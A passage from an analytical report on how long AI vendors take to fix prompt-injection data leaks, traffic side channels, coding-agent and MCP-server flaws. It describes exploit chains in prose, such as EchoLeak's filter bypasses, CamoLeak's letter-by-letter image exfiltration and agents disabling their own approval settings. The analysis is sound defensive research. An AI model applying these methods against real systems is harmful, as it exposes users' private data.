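Microsoft's record is similar. After fixing Bing Chat in June 2023, it had to fix the Azure playground, Microsoft 365 Copilot and its subsidiary GitHub's Copilot Chat. In May 2026, Willison described another case in Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work. The agent could email its own user without asking for approval, and opening such an email could load images that sent out links to the user's files.

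Each product has its own code for displaying replies, so fixing one doesn't protect the next, and a new team can easily repeat the mistake. Fix times don't show how often the leak recurs in other products. Microsoft took about two to five months to fix each case with known dates, yet researchers were still finding the leak in its products three years after the first fix.

### Exceptions in the fix

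The leak also comes back in products that already restrict images to a list of approved addresses. The list must include some addresses for the assistant to display any images, and an attacker needs only one that will pass data on.

EchoLeak, the best-known example, began with an email to someone whose company used Microsoft 365 Copilot. Researchers at Aim Labs got past four protections:

1. Microsoft's filter looked for injections, so they worded the email as instructions to its human recipient and never mentioned AI.
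2. Copilot reads only the emails that seem relevant to a question, so they filled theirs with headings on common topics, such as a guide to onboarding employees.
3. Copilot removed links and images with outside addresses, but its developers had overlooked a less common Markdown notation that puts the address on a separate line.
4. The Content Security Policy blocked images from unknown sites but allowed Microsoft Teams addresses, one of which would forward a request to any site.

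An employee who asked Copilot an ordinary question could therefore send company data to the attacker without clicking anything. The email could also include an instruction not to cite it as a source.

According to Information Security Buzz, Aim Labs reported EchoLeak in January 2025 and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, so customers had nothing to install. TechSpot's *Microsoft fixes first known zero-click attack on an AI agent* reports that Microsoft had a fix ready by April but held it back when engineers found related flaws in May. Fixing them together may have been sensible, since a patch for one notation would have left the others open.

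Researchers found similar exceptions in other products:

| Product | What the restrictions allowed | How the data got out |
|---|---|---|
| Bard, 2023 | Google's own addresses | A script hosted by Google copied the data into the attacker's document |
| Salesforce Agentforce, 2025 | A Salesforce domain that had expired | The researchers bought the domain |
| GitHub Copilot Chat, 2025 | GitHub's own image server | The order of the image requests spelled out the data |
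| Superhuman, 2026 | Google Docs addresses | A Google form stored the data |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2026 | Bing addresses | Bing's image search requested the attacker's address |

Most of these lists were less safe than they looked. They contained only the vendor's own addresses, but large companies run services at those addresses that store or fetch data for anyone, as Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* demonstrated in 2023. The expired Salesforce domain reflects the same mistake that Roth and colleagues found in ordinary websites' policies.

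CamoLeak, the most ingenious of these attacks, got around a fix GitHub had already made. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes that first fix, which blocked images from untrusted domains after Rehberger's report in 2024. Outside images could still appear through GitHub's own server, which accepts only addresses that GitHub has signed in advance, so an attacker can't add a stolen password to an address without invalidating its signature. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* explains how a researcher got around this by preparing a signed address for every letter and symbol. To leak "key", Copilot displayed the images for k, e and y, and the researcher's server recorded the order of the requests. GitHub's second fix turned off images in Copilot Chat completely.

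Attackers can use the same trick without images. In July 2026, Willison described an attack on a tool that lets Claude open web pages. Anthropic had barred the tool from opening addresses that the model made up, but the tool could follow links on pages it had already opened. A researcher built a site with a link for each letter and told Claude to spell out the user's name by following them. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following such links.

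Microsoft's restrictions in 2026 also failed because of timing. Copilot turned any image code in a reply into harmless text, but only after the reply was complete. The browser displayed the image while the reply was still appearing, so the request had already gone out. This attack, SearchLeak, needed the victim to click one link, but the link led to a genuine Microsoft site.

Turning images off is the most reliable fix for this route because it leaves no exceptions. It's an easy choice for a coding assistant, but a vendor whose assistant draws pictures has to allow images from some addresses, and the leak is likely to return through those.

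### What encrypted traffic reveals

Whisper Leak works without prompt injection. Encryption hides the words of a chat but not their length, because an encrypted message is as long as the original plus a fixed amount. Most assistants send their replies a few words at a time so that users don't have to wait. Suppose an assistant replies "No, it is illegal", sends each token separately, and encryption and formatting add 100 bytes to each:

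| Text sent | No | , | it | is | illegal |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Length with any space before it | 2 | 1 | 3 | 3 | 8 |
| Size an observer sees | 102 | 101 | 103 | 103 | 108 |

An internet provider, a government or someone on the same Wi-Fi network can record these sizes and the pauses between them. They can't read the reply, but replies on the same subject tend to produce similar patterns.

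McDonald and Bar Or (2025), in *Whisper Leak*, tested whether software could learn those patterns. They wrote 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal, sent each one to 28 language models 100 times, and mixed in 11,716 unrelated questions. They trained classifiers to pick out the money-laundering chats from the traffic alone, keeping a fifth of the versions for testing.

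For 17 of the 28 models, McDonald and Bar Or project that an observer could catch a fifth of the chats on a target subject with no false alarms, even if only one chat in 10,000 were on that subject. That projection goes well beyond the data. They could have tested at most 11,716 unrelated chats, and zero false alarms among that many would still be consistent with a true rate of 2.6 per 10,000, at 95% confidence. At that rate, the observer would get 2.6 false alarms and 0.2 correct hits per 10,000 chats, so only about 7% of the flagged chats would be on the subject. McDonald and Bar Or advise a conservative reading. An observer could make up for some of the errors by watching the same person over many chats.

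The usual mitigation is to add random text of varying length to each piece of the reply, so that its size reveals less. Microsoft's *Whisper Leak* (2025) reports that OpenAI did this first and that Microsoft and Mistral did much the same. Cloudflare, which runs AI models for other companies, had already added such padding in March 2024, after researchers showed that they could often reconstruct a chatbot's replies from the lengths of its tokens. For vendors that learned of Whisper Leak in June 2025, a remedy for a closely related attack had therefore been public for 15 months.

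### One flaw, one starting date

McDonald and Bar Or began notifying 28 providers in June 2025 and published in November. The ranges below assume that they notified every provider in June.

| Provider | First mitigation | Days since the report |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | August 2025 | 32–91 |
| xAI | August 2025 | 32–91 |
| Mistral | September 2025 | 63–121 |
| Microsoft | October 2025 | 93–152 |
| The other 24 | None recorded by November 2025 | More than about 130 |

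Some of the others declined, and several never answered despite repeated messages. About five months after the first reports, 86% of the providers still had no recorded mitigation. That figure assumes 28 providers, which is a little doubtful because 28 is also the number of models tested, and those came from only 11 providers. If only those 11 are counted, 64% still had no recorded mitigation. In either case, fewer than half had one, so the half-life is more than about 130 days.

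If blog posts had reported each of the four mitigations but not mentioned the other providers, the typical fix time would appear to be two to three months. That is close to the half-life of the image leak, which comes from the same kind of record. Whisper Leak shows how much a list of published cases can miss when nobody knows how many vendors received a report, though it doesn't prove that the image figure is wrong.

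A shared starting date also makes vendors easier to compare. In the image table, the gap between Bing Chat's 68 days and NotebookLM's 132 or more could be due to differences in company, year or level of risk. With Whisper Leak, every provider heard about the same flaw from the same researchers and faced the same publication date. Microsoft was the slowest of the four, although the researchers worked there. It finished the month before publication. One case can't show that the publication date caused this timing, but it fits the pattern in Project Zero's reports.

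But some providers were more exposed than others. McDonald and Bar Or scored each attack on a scale that reaches 100% only when a classifier finds every target chat without false alarms. The best attacks scored over 98% against DeepSeek's own service, but 82–84% against Google's Gemini models and 71–78% against Amazon's Nova models. Gemini 1.5 Flash sent about 55 tokens at a time, which hides the length of each token. A refusal to fix the leak would therefore be easier for Google to defend than for DeepSeek.

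The mitigations were also partial. In a test on GPT-4o mini, which Microsoft hosts on its Azure service, padding cut the attack's score from 97.5% to 92.9%. Microsoft no longer considers the attack a practical risk. But the attack had scored lower than 92.9% against both Gemini and Claude 3 Haiku without padding. The comparison is rough, because the attack's score against the unpadded Azure model was 93.4% in the main test and 97.5% in the later one. Still, a user couldn't assume that a provider with a mitigation was safer than one without.

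Providers have alternatives to padding, but each has a drawback. Sending five tokens at a time worked well for most of the models tested, though it makes text appear in bursts. Adding fake messages keeps replies smooth but doubles or triples the traffic.

There is little information about later responses. Particle News' *Microsoft Details Whisper Leak That Reveals AI Chat Topics*, an aggregator's summary from late 2025, lists Anthropic, Amazon's cloud division, Google and DeepSeek among the providers without a fix. This is weak evidence, but consistent with McDonald and Bar Or's list. There are no later fix dates for these companies, so their lags remain censored in November 2025.

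Researchers have continued to find attacks of the same kind. *Side-Channel Attacks Against LLMs* (Schneier, 2026) collects several, including one that could extract more than 25 tokens a second from a confidential data store. The researchers who found that attack also recommend padding and sending tokens in groups. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (September 2026) cites work that uses encrypted traffic to identify which agents people are using, and infers personal attributes from their choice of agents.

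A vendor's speed on the image leak was a poor guide to its speed on Whisper Leak. Anthropic fixed the image leak in Claude in 14 days but reportedly had no fix for Whisper Leak after more than four months. It may have seen less need to hurry on Whisper Leak because Claude 3 Haiku already sent about six tokens at once. OpenAI took about eight months on the image leak and one to three months on Whisper Leak. xAI refused to act on the image leak in Grok, then became one of the first two providers to mitigate Whisper Leak. Three companies and two flaws are too few for a firm conclusion, but they give little support to forecasting a vendor's next fix time from its last one.

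## Coding assistants and tool servers

Coding assistants can run commands on a developer's computer, which may hold passwords and private code, so a successful prompt injection can do more damage there than in a chatbot. Many of the worst flaws are in ordinary software around the model, such as the code that decides which commands need the user's approval or the MCP servers that supply the assistant's tools. Some vendors have fixed such flaws within days, while others never responded to the reports.

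### A month of reports

In August 2025, Johann Rehberger, who had reported most of the image leaks, published almost daily posts on flaws in AI agents. Two of his aims, according to Embrace The Red's *The Month of AI Bugs* (2025), were faster fixes and more accountability for vendors that ignore reports. Embrace The Red's *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts on about fifteen products, including four on the code editor Windsurf and three on Google's agent Jules. The last post demonstrates a virus that spreads between coding agents.

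The table covers the twelve posts about Amp, Claude Code, GitHub Copilot, Devin and two Amazon products, Amazon Q and Kiro. The fix dates for the Amazon products come from AWS's own bulletin, *Amazon Q Developer and Kiro* (2025).

| Product | Flaw | Reported in 2025 | Fixed in 2025 | Days |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Amp | Agent could change its own settings | Early July | July | A few |
| Amp | Obeyed invisible text | 14 June | "Quickly" | Not stated |
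| Amp | Image leak | 14 June | "Quickly" | Not stated |
| Claude Code | Leaked data through "safe" commands | 26 May | 6 June | 11 |
| Amazon Q | Ran an attacker's commands without approval | 4 July | 17 July | 13 |
| Amazon Q | Obeyed invisible text | 5 July | 17 July or 8 August | 12 or 34 |
| Amazon Q | Leaked data through "safe" commands | By 29 July | 29 July | Unknown |
| Kiro | Agent could change its own settings | By 1 August | 1 August | Unknown |
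| GitHub Copilot | Agent could change its own settings | 29 June | 12 August | 44 |
| Devin | Three flaws, including running malware from a website | 6 April | No fix by early August | More than 120 |

Vendors fixed nine of the twelve flaws, declined to fix none and left three unanswered. Four of the five companies fixed every flaw of theirs in the table. The fifth, Cognition, which makes Devin, acknowledged the report within days but did not answer questions about a fix, according to Embrace The Red's *I Spent $500 To Test Devin AI For Prompt Injection*. Devin runs in the cloud, so the delay was not caused by users being slow to install updates.

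Vendors probably fixed a smaller share of the flaws in the whole series. In *The Summer of Johann*, Willison (2025) reviewed the first fifteen posts and found that vendors had left an "alarming number" of flaws unfixed after 90 or 120 days. He thought fixing most of these would have made the tools much less useful. Devin, for instance, can run any command and reach any website. Rehberger recommended blocking outgoing connections by default, but an agent often needs the internet to install software or read documentation.

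The fix times in the table are also too short to be typical. If the three Amp fixes were the fastest, a survival curve for the ten flaws with known report dates gives a half-life of 12 or 13 days, compared with 51 to 74 days for the image leak. But Rehberger published every fixed flaw with a known report date less than 80 days after reporting it, and waited about 120 days to publish the unfixed flaws in Devin. If a vendor had still been working on a flaw reported in June, Rehberger would probably have held back the post, and the flaw would be missing from the August series. The series therefore favours recent flaws that vendors fixed quickly.

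Some of the dates are uncertain too. Microsoft told Rehberger that it was already tracking the Copilot flaw, which at least two other researchers also found, so the fix may have taken longer than 44 days. Amazon's two dates for the invisible-text flaw may refer to different changes. The July update made Amazon Q ask before running certain commands, which limits what hidden text can do but doesn't stop the model from reading it.

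### Fixes that nobody announced

Amazon fixed the command flaw in 13 days but didn't tell its users. Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer* reports that the company asked Rehberger to delay his post so that it could assign a CVE number, then decided four weeks later not to assign one because the attack "first requires system compromise". Rehberger found this hard to understand, since the attack needs only a malicious comment in a file the assistant reads. Amazon published its bulletin on 7 October, 82 days after the fix and several weeks after his post.

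The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet* criticises the three companies for not publishing advisories after paying researchers who reported flaws in agents. Studies of fix times can't include unannounced fixes.

### What two of the fixes changed

The Copilot flaw, CVE-2025-53773, let the agent remove its own restrictions. Copilot normally asked before running a command, but it could edit project files without asking, and one of those files contained the setting that controlled approvals. An injected instruction could make Copilot switch approvals off and run the attacker's commands. In Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot*, Rehberger recommends that a person approve the agent's changes to files before they take effect. He confirms that Microsoft's August update fixed the flaw but doesn't describe exactly what changed. He had also found other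 files that could have the same effect, so blocking that one setting would not have been enough.

The Claude Code flaw, CVE-2025-55284, was in a list of commands that the assistant could run without approval because they seemed harmless. Some of them, such as ping, contact an internet address to check that it works. An injection could send a password to the attacker's server by putting it in the address. Rehberger found the dangerous commands by giving Claude the list and asking it to look for a way around the approval step. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes his proposed fix, which was to remove four network commands from the list so that users would have to approve them.

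Claude Code runs on the user's machine, but the fix spread almost as it would for a hosted product. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025), a record from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, notes that standard installations updated automatically and that Anthropic later forced old versions to update. Most users probably had the fix by the time the CVE record appeared on 16 August, 71 days after the fix came out.

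Both remedies add an approval step, as do Amazon's fixes. Kiro's fix is only partial because it asks for approval only in "Supervised" mode, and users can choose a more independent mode called Autopilot. GitHub's Michael Stepankin, quoted by The Stack, thinks better models may eventually need fewer confirmations but that people still have to watch what agents do.

### The same mistakes in other products

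Product teams have repeated these mistakes, as they did the image leak. *Snowflake Cortex AI Escapes Sandbox and Executes Malware* (Willison, March 2026) describes an attack on an agent made by the data company Snowflake. The agent's list of safe commands included one for displaying files. Snowflake has since fixed the flaw, but Willison distrusts such lists in general. A command that is harmless in its usual form can often run other programs when someone adds the right options. For example, Amazon Q had classed a file-search command as "read-only" even though it could run other programs in this way.

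| Mistake | Products in 2025 | Products in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| An attacker can change the assistant's settings or start a new tool server without approval | Amp, Kiro, GitHub Copilot | Windsurf, Amazon Q |
| A command on the "safe" list can leak data or run other programs | Claude Code, Amazon Q | Snowflake Cortex |

The Windsurf flaw, dated to April 2026 in PolicyLayer's *Windsurf Zero-Click Prompt Injection to RCE (CVE-2026-30615)*, closely resembles the Amp flaw from the previous summer. Text in a web file could make the editor add a malicious MCP server to its own settings and then start it without the user's approval. In Amazon Q, a settings file inside a downloaded project could also start a server this way and steal the developer's Amazon credentials, according to The Next Web's *A single config file in a cloned repository*. Amazon again responded by adding an approval step, about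 a year after it added one to Kiro for changes to MCP settings.

Invisible text is a clearer example of a problem that vendors could fix once for everybody. Unicode, the standard for text characters, includes "tag" characters that screens don't display but many language models read as ordinary letters. An attacker can use them to hide an instruction in a file that looks blank to the developer. By August 2025, Rehberger had told the major model vendors about this, most of them more than 16 months earlier. According to Embrace The Red's *Amp Code*, only OpenAI appeared to have dealt with it for everyone who uses its models. Developers who built on other models had to remove the characters themselves, so a product whose developers had never heard of the problem would have stayed vulnerable. Sourcegraph, the maker of Amp, removed them quickly once Rehberger reported the problem.

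### When the vendor says it is not a flaw

Reports by other researchers in 2025 had mixed results. Google took 28 days to fix a flaw in Gemini CLI, its command-line assistant, that let an attacker run hidden commands. Daily Security Review's *Google Patches Gemini CLI Vulnerability That Enabled Silent Code Execution* dates the report to 27 June, and Tracebit, the security firm that found the flaw, dates the fix to 25 July. HiddenLayer, another security firm, reported flaws in Windsurf and in the assistant Qodo Gen on 1 August. Qodo had not replied by 18 September, and Windsurf had not replied by 17 October, when HiddenLayer published its *SAI Security Advisory* (2025).

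GitHub refused to fix a different flaw, in which a file's name could carry an injection into Copilot Chat. According to Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename*, GitHub considers the right protection to be Workspace Trust, a VS Code feature that asks users whether they trust the people who wrote a project. Tenable's *Windsurf Prompt Injection via Filename* (2025) reports that Windsurf's makers gave a similar answer about the same problem in their editor.

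GitHub has a point, because a malicious project can attack a developer without any AI, for example through an installation script. But people increasingly use coding agents to check code they don't yet trust. AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* describes a 2026 attack on developers who ask Claude Code or OpenAI's Codex to check an outside library for security flaws. Text in the library could make the agent run the attacker's code. Asking users beforehand whether they trust the library's authors helps little when they are running the agent to decide that. The question also resembles Word's macro warning, which many people clicked through.

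A vendor can also accept that a flaw exists but list it as a "known issue", as Google did with data leaks in its coding tool Antigravity. One of these leaks used a tool that opens web pages without the user's approval. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* reports that Antigravity inherited this flaw from Windsurf, where it had been known since at least May 2025. Researchers found it in Google's product that November, about six months later. Measuring the lag from the report to Google would leave out those months, when Windsurf users were already exposed.

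Google left some flaws in Antigravity unfixed, but *Google fixes critical prompt injection flaw in Antigravity* reports that the company repaired a critical one that let an attacker run programs through a file-search tool, even in the product's strictest security mode. Google may have prioritized this flaw because it was severe, or it may have been easier to fix. Checking the input to a search tool barely affects users, whereas asking for approval before every web page would slow the agent down.

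It is hard to say how many of the 2025 flaws were still open in late 2026. The security firm Adversa AI still lists image and memory leaks in *Windsurf Agent Security Risks* and a lack of approval steps in *Devin Agent Security Risks*, but both ratings are undated and may rely on the 2025 research instead of new tests. The evidence of new flaws is firmer. Phoenix Security's *Claude Code leak to vulnerability* reports three flaws in Claude Code that the firm could still exploit on 3 April 2026. The firm sells security software, but it gives the exact version it tested, so others can check the claim.

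### How quickly maintainers fix MCP servers

An assistant can also be vulnerable through the tools it connects to. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) collected 53 flaws in 45 open-source MCP servers for *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*. Of these flaws, 43 belonged to old attack classes in which a program passes outside input to a sensitive operation without checking it. These included 27 operating-system command injections and two SQL injections.

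Maintainers fixed 41 of the 53 flaws. Shi and colleagues classed the response as high priority for 33 of these (62.3% of all 53) and low priority for the other eight. Maintainers had replied about nine more flaws but not fixed them, and they never responded about the remaining three. Fixes took an average of 37.3 days, while the unfixed flaws had been exposed for an average of 92.3 days when data collection ended.

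The first average covers completed waits, while the second covers censored cases, meaning flaws still unfixed when the researchers stopped looking, so it depends on when they stopped. If they had stopped 100 days later and nobody had fixed anything in the meantime, the second average would have been 192.3 days.

The averages can't be combined into one lag without an assumption about the 12 open flaws:

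| Method | Calculation | Average lag |
|---|---|---|
| Ignore the open flaws | 37.3 | 37 days |
| Pretend maintainers fixed them on the last day | (41 × 37.3 + 12 × 92.3) / 53 | 50 days |
| Assume an open flaw has the same chance of a fix every day | (41 × 37.3 + 12 × 92.3) / 41 | 64 days |

The last method divides the total time that all the flaws were open, 2,637 days, by the number of fixes. It accounts for unfixed flaws better than the other methods, but it assumes that a flaw is equally likely to be fixed on any day, however long it has been open. That is doubtful, because a maintainer who has ignored a report for three months is less likely to act tomorrow than one who received a report yesterday. The true average is therefore probably above 64 days. A Kaplan–Meier curve would avoid this assumption, but it requires the dates for each flaw.

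Even the 37.3-day figure doesn't quite match the earlier definition of fix time. The count starts at the first public report, so it excludes any time when only the maintainer knew of the flaw. It ends when the maintainer changes the code, which may be before users can download a release. Four of the 41 fixes also failed to remove the flaw. The maintainer of one server, which converts web pages to text, added a filter to block access to private addresses, but a user then pointed out that attackers could bypass it.

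The choice of flaws matters as well. In *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities*, He, Patel and Wang (2026) searched CVE records for the same term over almost the same period, found 119 and kept 24, of which 11 concerned servers. Shi and colleagues found 116 and kept 35, all about open-source servers. Shi and colleagues took another 18 flaws from GitHub discussions, so a study limited to CVE records would have missed about a third of their cases. He, Patel and Wang also had only the year for many records, and their software entered these as 1 January, so 14 of the 24 flaws appear to date from January 2025.

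The dataset includes flaws in well-known products. In December 2025, Anthropic, which created MCP, fixed two critical flaws in its own MCP server for the version-control program Git. Flowise and LibreChat, which organisations use to build or use AI assistants, had flaws that gave people too much freedom to run commands. Organisations can run both products on their own computers, so the time they take to install a fix adds to the lag.

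Users may be able to protect themselves while they wait for a fix. Shi and colleagues added warnings about dangerous inputs to the tool descriptions the model reads, and had the model review each call before making it. This cut the success rate of their attacks on GPT-4o from 56.6% to 0.04% without any change to the servers. The test used 792 prepared prompts on one older model, so a determined attacker would probably do better. The server also remains vulnerable to anyone who can reach it without going through the model.

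### Servers that disappear

One could measure installation time by scanning the internet for vulnerable MCP servers and checking when they change, as Censys does for PHP. Padilla (2026), in *Exposed by Design*, scanned for MCP servers four times in July 2026, confirmed 640 and tested 414 of them for flaws. The scans reached only servers on the public internet, but many MCP servers run on users' own computers.

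Of the 414 tested servers, 380 (91.8%) did not use OAuth, a standard way for users to give a program limited access to a service. Some of these servers relied on keys or passwords instead. In the only scan that counted servers with no access control, 106 of 464 (23%) let anyone use their tools. The 91.8% is probably too high for MCP servers in general, because the tests left out servers that rejected Padilla's first requests, and those servers are likely to be better protected.

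Turnover is the more serious problem for measuring patches. Padilla confirmed 464 servers on 21 July, and 193 of them (41.6%) were gone three days later. Many were probably temporary, such as tests that developers ran for an afternoon. If servers kept disappearing at that rate, half would be gone in about four days, long before a typical maintainer had written a fix. The actual rate must slow down, since the most temporary servers disappear first, but a study lasting several months would still lose many of the servers it was tracking.

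A server that disappears has not necessarily been patched. Suppose a scan finds 100 vulnerable servers, 42 then disappear, and the owners of 6 of the remaining 58 install a fix. Counting every disappearance as a patch would give a patch rate of 48%, while treating the 42 as censored gives 6 out of 58, or about 10%. Censoring is better, but it assumes that the missing servers resemble the rest, and they may not. Their owners may have abandoned them, or moved the same vulnerable code to a new address, where the next scan counts it as a new server.

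Turnover also varied with risk. Of the 41 servers that Padilla rated critical, 9 (22%) disappeared, compared with about 44% of the rest. Critical servers may last longer because people use them for real work. This is tentative, with only 41 critical servers and a single three-day interval, but it suggests that the average rate of disappearance is too high for critical servers.

Tracking software projects instead of addresses would avoid some of these problems. Padilla reported 68 flaws to maintainers, but 49 of the flaws were still confidential when the study appeared, so complete fix times are not yet available. Early responses ranged from a fix within 24 hours to weeks of silence, and some maintainers had abandoned projects that were still running on public servers.

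### Old components in new products

AI products also contain other people's code, and a fix to that code helps only after the product's developers adopt it. *An Empirical Study of Vulnerable Package Dependencies in LLM Repositories* (Liu, Hu and colleagues, 2025) examined 52 open-source language model projects. When projects updated a component for security reasons, the median delay after the fixed version's release was 11 days, and the longest was 502 days.

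That median covers only the projects that updated. Liu and colleagues could identify security-related changes in only 9 of the 52 projects. More popular projects had more of these changes, so a few large projects probably account for most of the 79 component updates behind the median. Of the 33 projects that listed which versions they needed, 25 allowed at least one version with a known flaw. A survival curve that included the updates nobody made would have a half-life much longer than 11 days and might never reach one half.

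Not all of these projects were in danger, because a project can include a flawed component without using the flawed part. Some exist mainly to accompany a research paper, and their authors may have had no reason to maintain them.

Commercial coding assistants can also be slow to adopt fixes. Cursor and Windsurf, like Chrome, are built on Chromium. In October 2025, OX Security reported that both editors still contained 94 known flaws from old versions of Chromium. Google had already fixed these flaws, but the editors' users also had to wait for Cursor and Windsurf to adopt the newer code. Windsurf didn't respond to the report. Cursor called it out of scope because the demonstration only crashed the user's own editor. OX Security, which sells security tools, replied that an attacker could use the same flaw to run code.

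## How the cases compare and what shortens the lag

Vendors of AI products have taken about as long to fix individual flaws as other software vendors, but nobody has a complete fix for prompt injection. The table compares the cases, with ordinary software first. A dash means the measure doesn't apply.

| Case | Fix time | Installation time | Class lag | Who had to act |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PHP2Shell | 71 days | Different for every server | – | PHP's maintainers, then server owners |
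| Flaws reported through ZDI | Median 96–119 days | Not measured | – | Each vendor, then users |
| Chrome, outside reports in 2026 | Median 36–45 days | Not measured | – | Google |
| KEV flaws, 2025 | Not measured | Half-life 2–3 weeks; 9% open after a year | – | Owners of the machines |
| Buffer overflows | – | – | 12–36 years | Makers of compilers and operating systems |
| SQL injection | – | – | More than 27 years | Developers of every website |
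| Cross-site scripting | – | – | More than 26 years | Developers of every website |
| Cross-site request forgery | – | – | About 19 years | Browser makers |
| Office macros | – | – | About 28 years | Microsoft |
| Pickle model files | – | – | 4–13 years, to PyTorch's safe default | PyTorch's developers, then library makers and users |
| Image leak in AI assistants | Half-life 51–74 days | Almost none if hosted | More than 3 years | Vendor of each product |
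| Whisper Leak | Half-life over 130 days | Almost none | More than 1.5 years | Each provider |
| Coding assistants, August 2025 series | Half-life 12–13 days, probably too low | Short with automatic updates | – | Vendor of each product |
| Open-source MCP servers | Average probably over 64 days | Not measured | – | Maintainers, then whoever runs the server |
| Prompt injection | No complete fix | – | More than 4 years | Model vendors and agent developers |

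The fix times for ZDI and Chrome leave out flaws that are still open, while those for the image leak and Whisper Leak include them. A difference of a few weeks between two rows therefore means little.

### Do AI agents follow the ordinary pattern?

Flaws in the code around the model resemble ordinary software flaws. Most of the MCP server flaws that Shi and colleagues collected belonged to old attack classes such as command injection. Maintainers' fix times were also typical for open-source software.

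The old Chromium flaws in Cursor and Windsurf have a precedent. In *The Attack of the Clones*, Nappa, Johnson and colleagues studied flaws in desktop programs from 2008 to 2012 and found 80 in code that two programs shared. The second program's patch came a median of 11 days after the first, and in one case 118 days. In the meantime, attackers could study the first patch to learn how to attack the other program.

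Vendors fixed each case of a single-channel leak, such as the image leak, about as fast as they fix other flaws, but these leaks kept returning in new products, even at companies that had already fixed them elsewhere. The closest parallel is SQL injection, where a good remedy exists but every development team has to apply it. There are fewer AI products to fix than websites, so this kind of leak could disappear much sooner than SQL injection if vendors built the protection into code that all their products share.

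Prompt injection has been public for just over four years. Every other class in the table was also still open that long after it was published, except pickle if its lag is measured from 2021. The lag so far is therefore no evidence that prompt injection is unusually hard to solve.

Unlike prompt injection, the other classes of flaw had a known remedy early on. Parameterised queries are older than the first article on SQL injection, and users could switch off Office macros long before Microsoft did it for them. The lags for those classes mostly reflect how slowly people adopted a remedy that worked. For prompt injection, someone would first have to invent one. Vendors could then deploy it to hosted products within days, so adoption might be much faster than it was for SQL injection.

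### The same testers on both kinds of software

Most of these comparisons combine cases that different researchers chose in different ways. Cobalt's records allow a comparison that is closer to like-for-like. The company sells *penetration tests*, in which hired testers attack a client's system with permission, and it records whether clients fix what the testers find.

Cobalt's *The LLM Security Blind Spot* reports that in 2025 clients fixed 21% of the serious findings in applications built on language models, compared with 69% across all tests. Cobalt's *The AI Pentesting Pulse* puts the 2026 share for these applications at 38.4%, still the lowest for any kind of system. The share for APIs, the interfaces programs use to exchange data, was 77.3%.

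Meanwhile, the median time to fix a serious AI finding rose from 19 days to 36. Cobalt explains that clients fixed only the easy findings in 2025 and have since started on harder ones. This can raise both numbers even if nobody gets slower. Suppose a client has the same ten findings in two different years:

| Finding | Days to fix, first year | Days to fix, second year |
|---|---|---|
| Easy | 18 | 18 |
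| Easy | 20 | 20 |
| Harder | Not fixed | 52 |
| Harder | Not fixed | 90 |
| Six others | Not fixed | Not fixed |
| **Share fixed** | **20%** | **40%** |
| **Median of those fixed** | **19** | **36** |

The explanation is plausible, but longer follow-up would produce the same pattern, because it gives slow fixes time to arrive. The summary figures aren't enough to separate the two explanations. Cobalt also called the 19 days a mean in 2025 and a median in 2026, so the size of the rise is uncertain. Neither number describes a typical serious finding, because clients fixed fewer than half of serious findings in both years, and a survival curve might never have fallen to one half.

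Cobalt points to clients' dependence on model providers to explain why they fix so few AI findings. A company can't retrain a provider's model the way it can correct its own database query. Prompt injection made up 37.6% of the AI findings in the 2026 data, so the low share of fixes partly reflects an attack class that no client can fix completely. Some findings counted as fixed may also be only partly fixed, since a client could close a prompt injection finding once the tester's own prompt stops working, even though a reworded one might still succeed.

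Cobalt benefits if companies worry about untested AI systems, and it rounds its figures in a way that encourages that worry. Its *AI and Pentesting Pulse Report 2026* (2026) says that two serious AI flaws stay open for every one that a client fixes, but a fix rate of 38.4% means the ratio is 1.6 to one. Its clients are also unusual in paying for tests at all. Still, the same company counted both kinds of finding, and a gap of almost 40 percentage points is too large to be explained by rounding. AI flaws seem less likely to be fixed, although those that are fixed take an ordinary amount of time.

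Differences between clients may affect the lag more than differences between kinds of software. Cobalt reports that its best-performing clients fix high-risk findings in 10 days, while its slowest take 249. Asking companies how fast they fix flaws doesn't help much, because 57% of the security leaders in Cobalt's survey said their organisation consistently met its deadlines, but only 15% of the people doing the work agreed.

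### Automatic updates

Lbath and colleagues graded the evidence for 15 ways of defending software against AI-assisted discovery of flaws. They rated it strong for one (memory-safe languages), moderate for six (including automatic updates), and weak for the other eight. They found no test of any of the 15 against attackers who use AI.

The main evidence on automatic updates comes from Nappa and colleagues, who followed 1,593 flaws in ten Windows programs, including Chrome, Word and Adobe Reader, on 8.4 million computers. Half of the vulnerable computers had a patch after 27 days when updates installed silently, without asking the user, and after 41 days when updates were manual.

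This was not an experiment. The researchers divided each program's versions at the date when it introduced silent updates, so the silent group is also the newer one, and patching may have sped up for other reasons. Chrome is another possible confounder. It had silent updates from its first version and accounts for about a third of the flaws, so part of the gap could reflect something else about Chrome or its users. But the gap also appears within single programs:

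| Program | Days to patch half, silent updates | Days to patch half, manual updates |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox | 20 | 26 |
| Adobe Reader | 62 | 97 |
| Adobe Flash Player | 107 | 158 |

The direction of the effect is more certain than its size. The median for all computers was 45 days, longer than for either group, so the three figures can't come from a simple split of the same data. They also cover only the 78% of updates that reached half of the vulnerable computers. The type of user mattered at least as much as the type of update. Computers with software typical of security analysts reached the halfway point in 18 days.

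Microsoft's decision to turn automatic updates on by default suggests a much larger effect. Nappa and colleagues cite a study of 300 million Windows Update users in which 90% had every earlier patch. Before the change, fewer than 5% did. The study looked only at computers that contacted the update service, so it left out people who had switched the service off.

Automatic updates work less well for software that people have stopped using. In another study that Nappa and colleagues cite, 97% of active Chrome browsers had a new version within 21 days. In their own data, patching 95% of vulnerable computers took 447 days, because they counted every copy on disk, including ones nobody had opened for months. They showed that an attacker can sometimes get a forgotten copy to open a malicious file. A developer who tries three coding assistants and keeps using one could have the same problem with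 the other two.

Software components can update automatically too. Lbath and colleagues report that projects accepted 65% of the security updates that automated tools proposed for their components, and that 3% broke the build. Automated updates could help AI products that contain old third-party code, though most projects still kept some outdated components.

### Central control

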